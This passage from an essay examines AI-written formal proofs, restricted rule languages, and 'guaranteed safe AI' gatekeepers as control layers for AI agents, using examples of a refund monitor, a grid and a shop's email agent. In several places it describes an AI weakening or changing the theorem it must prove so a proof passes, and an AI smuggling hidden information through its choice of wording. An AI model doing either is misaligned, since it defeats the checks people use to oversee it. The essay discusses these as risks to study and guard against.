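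The kernel could still have a bug, as Atelier B's prover did, and an AI that makes thousands of attempts may be more likely than a person to find it. Lean's creator, de Moura, points out that several independent kernels exist. A false proof would have to pass every kernel that someone runs on it.

People still have to read the first four lines. Suppose an AI couldn't prove the theorem for a more complicated function and quietly added the assumption that the price is below zero. `Nat` is Lean's type for whole numbers from zero upwards, so no price meets that assumption, and Lean would accept a proof of any claim about such prices. Even without that assumption, the theorem doesn't cover negative refunds, like the one Cedar's solver might return.

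### Every input to 239 test programs

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes the larger of two projects that applied this method to widely used software. Working with a company called Theorem, Anthropic had its model Claude prove security properties for the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries.

The libraries all belong to OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that looks for bugs by fuzzing, in which a small test program runs a library on many generated inputs to see whether any cause a crash. According to OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), the researchers automatically converted these tests into formal specifications, and Claude then proved that no input could cause a failure. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry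 Points* (2026) reports that the proofs cover 239 test programs and all inputs under 64 MB. The number of such inputs has more than 150 million digits, so fuzzing could never try them all.

*Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) and OpenNET give the same total. OpenNET also gives about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or 33 lines of proof per instruction. *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) mentions a billion lines, but 239 proofs of 600,000 lines each would total 143 million, which is much closer to 180 million. A person reading one line a second for eight hours a day would need 17 years to read 180 million lines, but only the proof checker has to go through them all.

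Claude also found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files. Some of the proofs therefore apply to repaired versions, and anyone still running the old code doesn't get the guarantee.

According to EconoTimes, the proofs establish that a program exits normally, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion (a check that the programmers wrote into the code). On this wording, they guarantee termination, even though the code is in languages that allow endless loops. They are otherwise similar to Astrée's proofs about Airbus software and don't establish that the output is correct, so an image library that turned every picture black would pass. OpenNET reports one proof that went further and showed that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, a compression library, conforms to the published standard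 for its format.

The guarantee applies to machine code for RISC-V processors, linked with a simple C library called musl. Anthropic acknowledges that most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM processors with a different C library, glibc. In *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, Leip (2026) reports that musl's function for comparing two pieces of text has 14 instructions and four jumps on RISC-V, while glibc's has 316 instructions and 45 jumps on the x86 processor studied.

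Leip's team started in mid-September 2026 and by the end of October had a proof about a complete x86 program with glibc. The proof assumes one particular processor, an operating system on which memory requests always succeed, and no outside interference. The theorem also allows the program to crash during startup, before it reaches its own code.

OpenNET reports that researchers on Anthropic's project also generated an interpreter for a subset of Python, written in Rust, and used a tool called Verus to verify it. This is closer to a control layer, since CaMeL relies on this kind of interpreter to track where an agent's data came from. A proof that such an interpreter never loses a label would rule out leaks like the one through a skipped assignment, and plans could still be written in Python.

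### Signal's encryption, down to machine code

In November 2026, Google DeepMind's *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) proved a more demanding kind of property for parts of libsignal, the code that encrypts messages in the app Signal. The proofs cover the handshake, in which two people's phones agree on a secret key, and the "Triple Ratchet", which keeps replacing the keys as they exchange messages. The proved properties include forward secrecy, which means a thief who steals today's keys can't read yesterday's messages, and post-compromise security, which means the conversation becomes secret again some time after a theft.

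An AI agent, guided by people, wrote the specification in Lean. The team also needed a precise description of AArch64, the machine language of 64-bit ARM processors. Other agents then searched for proofs without human help. A gatekeeper accepted a proof only if Lean's kernel checked it against the specification that people had approved. This check prevents an agent from making its job easier by changing the theorem.

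Chaudhuri and colleagues' technical report describes about 6.5 million lines of proof, which rest on about 26,000 lines of specification and processor description that people have to trust. That is about 250 lines of proof for each trusted line. The summary attached to DeepMind's announcement, *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026), gives only "over three million". The technical report's figure is more likely to be right, since the report accompanies the published proofs, and *AlphaProof Code* (Schock, 2026), an account of the announcement, also gives more than six million. According to Schock, the process took four weeks, and people had to review only about 1% of the code base.

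EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) explains that the team verified a small program that is built around libsignal and handles conversations between two people. The proofs don't cover the whole library.

DeepMind tested whether the 26,000 lines of specification could rule out insecure code by putting two old bugs back into a separate copy of the code. In both cases, the system proved that the copy was insecure. This is a good test because an empty specification would have held for the faulty copies too, although two known bugs are a small sample.

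In both projects, other people had already worked out most of what to prove. A crash means the same thing in any program, and cryptographers have spent decades defining forward secrecy. Few control layers have this advantage. For example, there is no comparable literature on which customers deserve a refund.

### Specifications that nobody has checked

The main criticism of AI-written proofs concerns this gap. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, argue that now that proofs are easy to produce, the bottleneck is specification and modelling. They work for Runtime Verification, a company that sells this expertise, but they give good examples.

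In some projects, an AI first rewrites a program in a proof language and then proves properties of its own version. Researchers asked Claude to describe how Etcd, a database that keeps copies of its data on several machines, gets the copies to agree. Claude returned essentially the algorithm from the original paper, which passed every check but bore little resemblance to Etcd's code. Across leading models, such descriptions scored nearly 100% for correct syntax but only about 46% for matching the actual program.

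An AI can also alter the statement it is supposed to prove. In one test, a system received a deliberately false piece of algebra: if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51. The correct value is 45. The system declared x to be a natural number, but no natural number satisfies 3^x = 5, so the false statement became provable, as it would with the negative price. In another study that Tolmach and Klaus cite, an agent got 89.5% of its formal statements to compile, but only 60.5% were faithful to the original mathematics. A second AI reviewer helps only partly. In one study, AI judges missed a quarter of the faulty specifications for Rust programs.

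The first problem has a fairly good answer. Anthropic and DeepMind worked from the compiled program itself, so no AI had to restate it. Their description of the processor could still be wrong, but people can test it against real chips and reuse it for every program. Andrews and Zhang (2026), in *Formalizing CPython*, used an easier method. They had Claude translate the functions of the standard Python interpreter into Lean, and tested each translation against real Python on tens of thousands of inputs before trying to prove anything. By November, 4,071 functions, covering 16% of the interpreter, had passed this test and a review by a second agent. The work produced 418 bug reports, about 55 of them for bugs that can crash Python or corrupt its memory. Tests can still miss a difference between the translation and the original.

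Some evidence on the second problem is encouraging. In *Agentic Proving for Program Verification*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) found that Claude wrote "arguably valid" specifications for 98.8% of the problems in the Clever benchmark. This doesn't contradict the much lower figures, because Clever contains short programming exercises with clear descriptions. An AI can probably formalise "no refund may exceed the price" reliably, but it will do worse on a forty-page refund policy whose writers disagreed about what it meant.

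Human experts get specifications wrong too. Cryspen, which develops verified cryptographic software, had claimed that nobody had found a bug in its verified code. Symbolic Software (2026), which was in a bitter public dispute with Cryspen, replied with three. Two were in the mathematical specification, and the third was in a correctness proof that Cryspen's documentation described as complete. Cryspen's *The strengths and limits of formal verification* gives a longer record for HACL*, an older library with 135,000 lines of generated code. In nine years, its developers twice found errors in the specifications. Users more often found bugs in 1,800 lines of supporting C code that the proofs didn't cover. That is an excellent record for the verified part, and it suggests looking for bugs in the new projects' specifications and in the code their proofs don't cover.

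Keles adds that when a proof took a team years, readers could rely on reputation and assume the proof wasn't trivial, but that assumption fails when anyone can produce a "formally verified" program in an afternoon. Keles wants people to stop using the phrase "formally verified" and always name the properties proved and the parts trusted, and credits Anthropic and DeepMind with doing so. This would especially help buyers of control software, since "verified monitor" could mean anything from "never crashes" to "follows the refund policy".

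### Rules that change next week

Suppose the specification is right. The shop writes its refund monitor in ordinary Rust, and an AI proves that the compiled program never approves more than 100 euros. The following week, the finance manager raises the limit to 150 euros for repeat customers. The old proof doesn't cover the new program, and the theorem is now false, so somebody has to restate the theorem before an AI can prove it. If the rule were in Cedar, the manager could edit one line and see an example of a refund that the edit newly allows, without stating any theorem.

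A proof applies to one program, while a restricted language's guarantees apply to every program written in it, including rules added later by people who have never used a proof assistant such as Lean.

Programmers can get around this to some extent by making the limit a setting. They would prove that the monitor never approves more than the limit, whatever the limit is, so the manager could change it without a new proof. But this only works for changes the programmers foresaw. To allow for repeat customers, they would need settings for groups of customers, then for exceptions, then for combinations of conditions. By that point the settings file is a small language, something like Cedar, and the monitor is its interpreter.

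AI-written proofs may therefore be most valuable for the checkers and interpreters of restricted languages, because a single proof benefits every program written in the language. Slides from Lean (2026) describe how Ilya Sergey of the National University of Singapore used Claude to help verify the borrow checker of Move, a language for programs that run on blockchains. The borrow checker rejects programs that misuse references to data. The proof is 39,000 lines long and took 27 working days, compared with an estimated five to six months without AI. Claude repaired proofs and handled routine cases, while Sergey supplied the new ideas.

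Checkers that haven't been proved correct are a serious weakness. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) tested ways of using language models to find errors that don't cause obvious crashes. One of the best, according to Faisal's *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (2026), was to ask Claude to prove a program correct and see where the proof failed. Rust's compiler is supposed to guarantee that ordinary Rust code never touches invalid memory. Claude found dozens of counterexamples, including a five-line program that reads memory after releasing it. That bug had been in the compiler for more than seven years. Claude also found over 100 flaws in Linux's eBPF verifier.

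Rust and Move both allow unbounded loops. Their checkers restrict how programs use memory, which is enough to guarantee memory safety for every program they accept, if the checkers are right. A shop that wants the same kind of guarantee about its refund rules needs a language that restricts what the rules can compute. The two approaches then compare as follows:

| | AI-written proof about one compiled program | Restricted rule language with an analyser |
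|---|---|---|
| After an edit | An AI has to repair the proof and may fail | A solver rechecks the rules, usually in under a second |
| What people must read | The theorem and the model of the machine | The rules, and any example the analyser finds |
| What must be correct | Theorem, machine model, proof checker, hardware | Rules, rule engine and its compiler, analyser, hardware |

Speed matters more when the rules change often. A monitor that changes twice a year can wait a week for a new proof, but Progent lets a model propose new rules in the middle of a task, so it needs an answer before the agent can continue. When an AI fails to find a proof, it is also hard to tell whether the program is wrong or the AI stopped searching too early.

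The restricted language is also easier to read, at least for simple rules. To prove that a Rust monitor follows the 100-euro rule, somebody has to state the rule in Lean, which takes about as much text as writing it in Cedar. The shop would then have a specification, a program and a proof that they agree, when it could have written the rule in Cedar and run that directly. The extra work makes sense for an encryption library, because forward secrecy is a statement about what attackers can learn, which can't be run as a program.

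Proofs about machine code have a smaller trusted computing base than Cedar does. They don't depend on the compiler, whereas Cedar's production engine is a Rust program that AWS tests but hasn't proved correct. An AI could now try to prove that the compiled engine behaves exactly like Cedar's Lean model. The model would serve as the specification, so nobody would have to write a new one.

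## Guaranteed safe AI: extending the proof to effects in the world

Cedar's analyser can show that no refund exceeds 100 euros, and an AI can prove that a compiled library never crashes. Neither result shows that the shop won't lose money or that nobody will get hurt. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) want proofs about effects like these. Proving that the shop loses at most 1% of its revenue to false claims, for instance, requires a description of the customers as well as the code.

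The design has three parts. The world model is a mathematical description of how the AI's actions affect its surroundings. The safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. The verifier uses the world model to check the AI's actions against the specification, and produces either a proof that they meet it or an upper bound on the probability of harm. An action goes ahead only if the verifier approves it. As in the Simplex architecture, approval doesn't depend on how the AI chose the action.

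The paper grades each part. World models range from trained simulators that nobody can inspect, through causal models audited by experts, to models proven to agree with the laws of physics. Verifiers range from improvised tests to proofs short enough for a person to read, and only the top three of the eleven grades count as giving a strong guarantee.

### A medicine that should never run out

Suppose an AI orders a medicine for a hospital's warehouse, which has unlimited space and now holds ten boxes of it. In the world model, the stock rises by one box each day with probability p and otherwise falls by one. Nobody knows p exactly, but it is at least 2/3. The specification requires the chance of the stock ever reaching zero to be below 0.1%.

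No test can run forever, so the AI submits a formula instead, V = (1/2)^x, where x is the number of boxes. The verifier checks two things. First, V equals 1 when the stock is zero. Second, V never rises on average from one day to the next. It halves with probability p and doubles otherwise, so its average the next day is

```
p * V/2 + (1 - p) * 2V = (2 - 1.5p) * V
```

which is at most V whenever p is at least 2/3. A quantity that is never negative and never rises on average can reach 1 with a probability no greater than its starting value. With ten boxes V starts at 1/1,024, so the chance of ever running out is just under 0.1%.

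Researchers call such a formula a certificate, and like a proof in Lean, it is easier to check than to find. A world model doesn't have to be exact. The one in this example gives probabilities for the daily changes but only a range for p, and the certificate is valid for every value in that range.

But if a supplier becomes unreliable and p drops to 1/2, the stock is certain to run out eventually, no matter how many boxes it started with, even though the certificate is still a correct proof about the old model.

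### Hardware that demands a proof

Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, extend proof-carrying code, which some researchers want to use for eBPF, to machines. Under their proposal, a chip would run a program only if the program came with a proof that it met agreed rules, and a drone would take off only with a proof that the flight was safe. Terrorists who used AI to design a virus would face a similar check at every stage, from the design software to the machine that makes the DNA.

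Tegmark and Omohundro expect that most of these programs won't be neural networks, which they consider too messy to verify. Instead, an AI would turn what a network has learned into ordinary code. Tegmark's talk *Provably Safe AI* describes an automated tool that did this for a network trained to add numbers. The researchers then proved that the extracted program adds any numbers correctly. Addition is a very easy case, though, because it already had a perfect specification.

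Tegmark and Omohundro's main argument is that even a superintelligent AI can't do what is provably impossible. This is true, but a proof shows only that something is impossible within a model. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that attackers have broken into formally verified systems through the physical properties of the hardware. To address this, Tegmark and Omohundro propose verifying the hardware too, but the proof would still apply only within a model, although a larger one.

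### ARIA's gatekeeper

Britain's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) has tried to put the idea into practice through a programme that has £59 million, according to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*. In the programme's original thesis, Dalrymple (2024) planned a "gatekeeper" built with the help of AI. AI systems would help experts write the world model and specification, search for certificates, and train an easy-to-verify controller. A small, formally verified program would check the certificates. If verification failed, a more cautious backup controller would take over.

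The plan called for new languages for world models, specifications and certificates, with design goals almost opposite to Cedar's. The modelling language had to cover continuous quantities, chance, ignorance and neural networks. The specification language had to express claims about what would otherwise have happened, such as a limit on the probability that the AI injures somebody who would have been unharmed if it had done nothing. Dalrymple and colleagues allow world models in Turing-complete languages. No algorithm can settle every question in languages this expressive, so the gatekeeper depends on an AI finding a certificate for each case.

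In November 2025, ARIA explained in *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that it had stopped the machine-learning part of the programme because it expected ordinary frontier models to acquire most of the necessary abilities anyway. It moved £18 million from that part to the tools. It then cancelled a planned second round of funding for physical applications and made cybersecurity the priority. Nora Ammann, who had by then replaced Dalrymple as director, adds in the revised thesis for *Safeguarded AI* (2026) that a timely international consensus on gatekeepers had become less likely.

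One team funded by ARIA has interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains, built mathematical models of their processes, and begun working with industrial partners. ARIA's accounts up to mid-2026 describe no physical system running under a safety guarantee, although the programme continues until the end of 2027. In the November interview, Dalrymple's favourite candidate for a demonstration was a formally verified firewall.

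ARIA attributes these changes to rapid progress in AI, not to a failure of world modelling, and its work on the modelling language continues. But a firewall is part of a control layer, so proving one correct is closer to DeepMind's work on Signal than to the original aim of guaranteeing effects in the physical world.

### Bodies, brains and misleading photographs

*Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (Andrew Dickson, 2024) gives the most detailed criticism. Engineers formally verified software for the lander that took the Perseverance rover to Mars, but the verification covered only bugs in the code. Dickson cites an estimate that software accounts for about a fifth of the risk of a Mars mission.

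Dickson argues that the threats people worry about most are much harder to model than a landing. To prove that a new virus is harmless, a verifier would need to predict its effects on a human body. In 2022, one of the most advanced simulations of its kind covered 20 minutes in the life of a single, unusually simple cell, and a body has about 36 trillion cells. In his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds estimates that verifying the safety of DNA would take a thousand years of progress in microbiology.

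Ammann's *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* replies that nobody needs such a simulation. Showing that none of the virus's proteins can get it into a human cell would be enough to rule out infection. This test would also reject some useful gene therapies, but false alarms are acceptable if it never misses a dangerous virus. This is a good answer to the demand for a simulated body, but it covers only one route to harm. Dickson had already mentioned that somebody could insert the DNA directly into a cell. Researchers would also have to prove that their model of proteins never overlooks a match. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest a more modest goal, a DNA machine that provably can't make certain known pathogens.

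Even a perfect model needs facts about the present, and sensors may not be able to supply them. Dickson points out that Google needed several years and 1.4 petabytes of data to map a millionth of a human brain. Ammann answers that a model can use ranges instead of exact measurements. In the warehouse example, if there could be anywhere from four to ten boxes, the verifier can assume four. The chance of running out is then at most 1/16, which is correct for that range but far above the required 0.1%, and the limit is wrong if there are actually only two boxes.

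Harm is also hard to define. A genuine photograph presented out of context can mislead people, so Dickson doubts that anyone could write a specification that rules out misinformation. Dalrymple and colleagues concede that "harm" has disputed borderline cases, and warn that a measurable substitute may stop tracking harm once an AI optimises for it. Ammann replies that a specification can forbid particular conditions, such as an overheated component, without capturing everything people value. This works where engineers already know which conditions are dangerous.

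### How much a probability can promise

Dickson reads the proposal as promising a failure rate of zero. Martinez Suñe replies that the specification can itself contain probabilities. Dalrymple and colleagues also show that if the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a system proved safe for n steps stays safe with probability at least (1 − ε)^n.

If a controller makes a decision every half hour and ε is 1 in 100,000, the formula gives 99.95% for a day but only 84% for a year. Ammann argues that guarantees over short periods are still useful. This is true if people use each period to compare the model with reality and correct it, but without those corrections, the daily guarantees still combine to only 84% over a year.

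Nobody can prove the value of ε either. To be 95% confident that it is below 1 in 100,000, engineers would need to observe about 300,000 half hours without an error. That would take about 17 years, during which the world would have to stay much the same.

Hatfield-Dodds similarly complains that a world model hasn't solved the problem but has "just moved it around a bit", because somebody must still show that the model matches reality. Ammann responds that every approach to AI safety relies on assumptions about the world, and that building a world model at least means writing them down where others can challenge them. This is an advantage only for assumptions that somebody can check.

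Dalrymple and colleagues make the more ambitious reply that an AI can threaten humanity only if it can make complicated plans that work reliably, and in that case the world must be predictable enough to model. But the AI needs to predict the results of only one plan, while a guarantee has to cover every plan it might try.

### Balancing an electricity grid

A grid suits the method well. In the original ARIA thesis, Dalrymple looked for problems that scientists already understand and that remain predictable despite small measurement errors. Ammann also names grids as a good fit.

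Britain's grid runs at 50 cycles per second (50 Hz). When a power station fails, the remaining generators slow down and the frequency drops. Suppose a shortfall of 1,000 MW, the output of the largest station, lowers the frequency by 0.125 Hz every second, and the specification requires the frequency to stay at or above 49.5 Hz if any one station fails. An AI proposes which stations to run and which batteries to hold in reserve.

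If the reserve rises steadily from zero to 1,000 MW over eight seconds, the average shortfall is 500 MW. The frequency drops by 8 × 0.0625 = 0.5 Hz and stops at exactly 49.5 Hz. The verifier should accept the plan only if the reserve reaches full power within eight seconds. If fewer heavy turbines are running, the frequency might drop twice as fast, which would cut the limit to four seconds. The verifier can assume this worse case, but the plan would then need faster batteries. It doesn't need to predict when each person will boil a kettle, because the total demand of millions of people stays within a fairly narrow range.

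On 9 August 2019, lightning struck a British power line. A wind farm, a gas-fired power station and many small generators disconnected almost together, removing nearly 1,900 MW of supply. The operator held only about 1,000 MW in reserve, so the frequency fell to 48.8 Hz. Automatic equipment then cut off more than a million customers, which stopped the fall and probably prevented a much larger blackout. A proof about the loss of any one power station would still have been correct, because it would not have covered several generators disconnecting together. A model of the grid alone would also have left out the dozens of trains that stopped because their own software shut them down at low frequency. Some of the trains needed a technician to restart them.

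### One layer among several

Safety engineers call the equipment that cut off those customers a layer of protection. They don't expect any layer to be perfect. If two layers each fail once in 100 emergencies, and the failures are independent, both fail in the same emergency once in 10,000. The calculation is wrong if the layers share a weakness, as the speed restrictions and the signallers' screen did on the Cambrian line.

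Engineers choose the layers through a hazard analysis, in which they list what could go wrong, estimate how likely and how serious each hazard is, and decide how to prevent it or limit the damage. A guardrail that addresses none of the listed hazards may work as designed without preventing any harm that matters. *The Application of Artificial Intelligence in Functional Safety*, a guide from the IET, a British engineering institution, covers hazard analysis right after its introduction.

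Dalrymple and colleagues accept much of this. They recommend several layers of defence, monitoring for signs that the world model is wrong, and a trustworthy backup system. On this view, the verifier is a strong layer, but other layers must handle whatever the world model omits. The specification should come from the hazard analysis.

### Answering the shop's email

Suppose the shop lets an agent answer its customers' email, and the specification is that no reply may lead to harm. The world model must then include the customers. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest describing people by a set of possible behaviours instead of predicting what they will do. But after reading instructions for cleaning a kettle, one customer in a million may put it in the sink while it is still plugged in. If the set includes this behaviour, the verifier has to reject the instructions and, for similar reasons, almost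 every other useful reply. If the set leaves it out, the guarantee doesn't cover that customer.

A reader of *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* asked how anyone could build a model of human psychology that never misses a possible reaction. Ammann already concedes in the article that natural language is too open-ended for this approach and that chatbots are a poor fit.

Ammann also considers an AI that hides something harmful inside an approved answer. The proposed defence is to prove that the answer is the only correct one, so that the AI can only give it or decline, which conveys a single bit. But an email has countless acceptable wordings. The shop could restrict the agent to 16 standard replies, which would limit each choice to four bits, but customers with unusual problems would then need help from staff.

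A hazard analysis is more useful to the shop because it identifies specific harms and a safeguard against each. The agent might send one customer's address to another, so the mail software should allow replies only to the person who wrote in and block any other customer's details. The agent might promise a refund the shop doesn't owe, so the payment system should ignore promises made by email. The agent might also give dangerous advice about a damaged kettle, so staff should answer questions about electrical safety. Software can enforce the first two measures without a model of the reader, but somebody still has to decide which questions are about electrical safety.

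The agent might also file a customer's report of an electric shock as a routine complaint. No check on outgoing email can catch this, because the harm comes from failing to send a warning. The shop could search incoming messages for words such as "shock", "smoke" and "burn", and have somebody read every match the same day.
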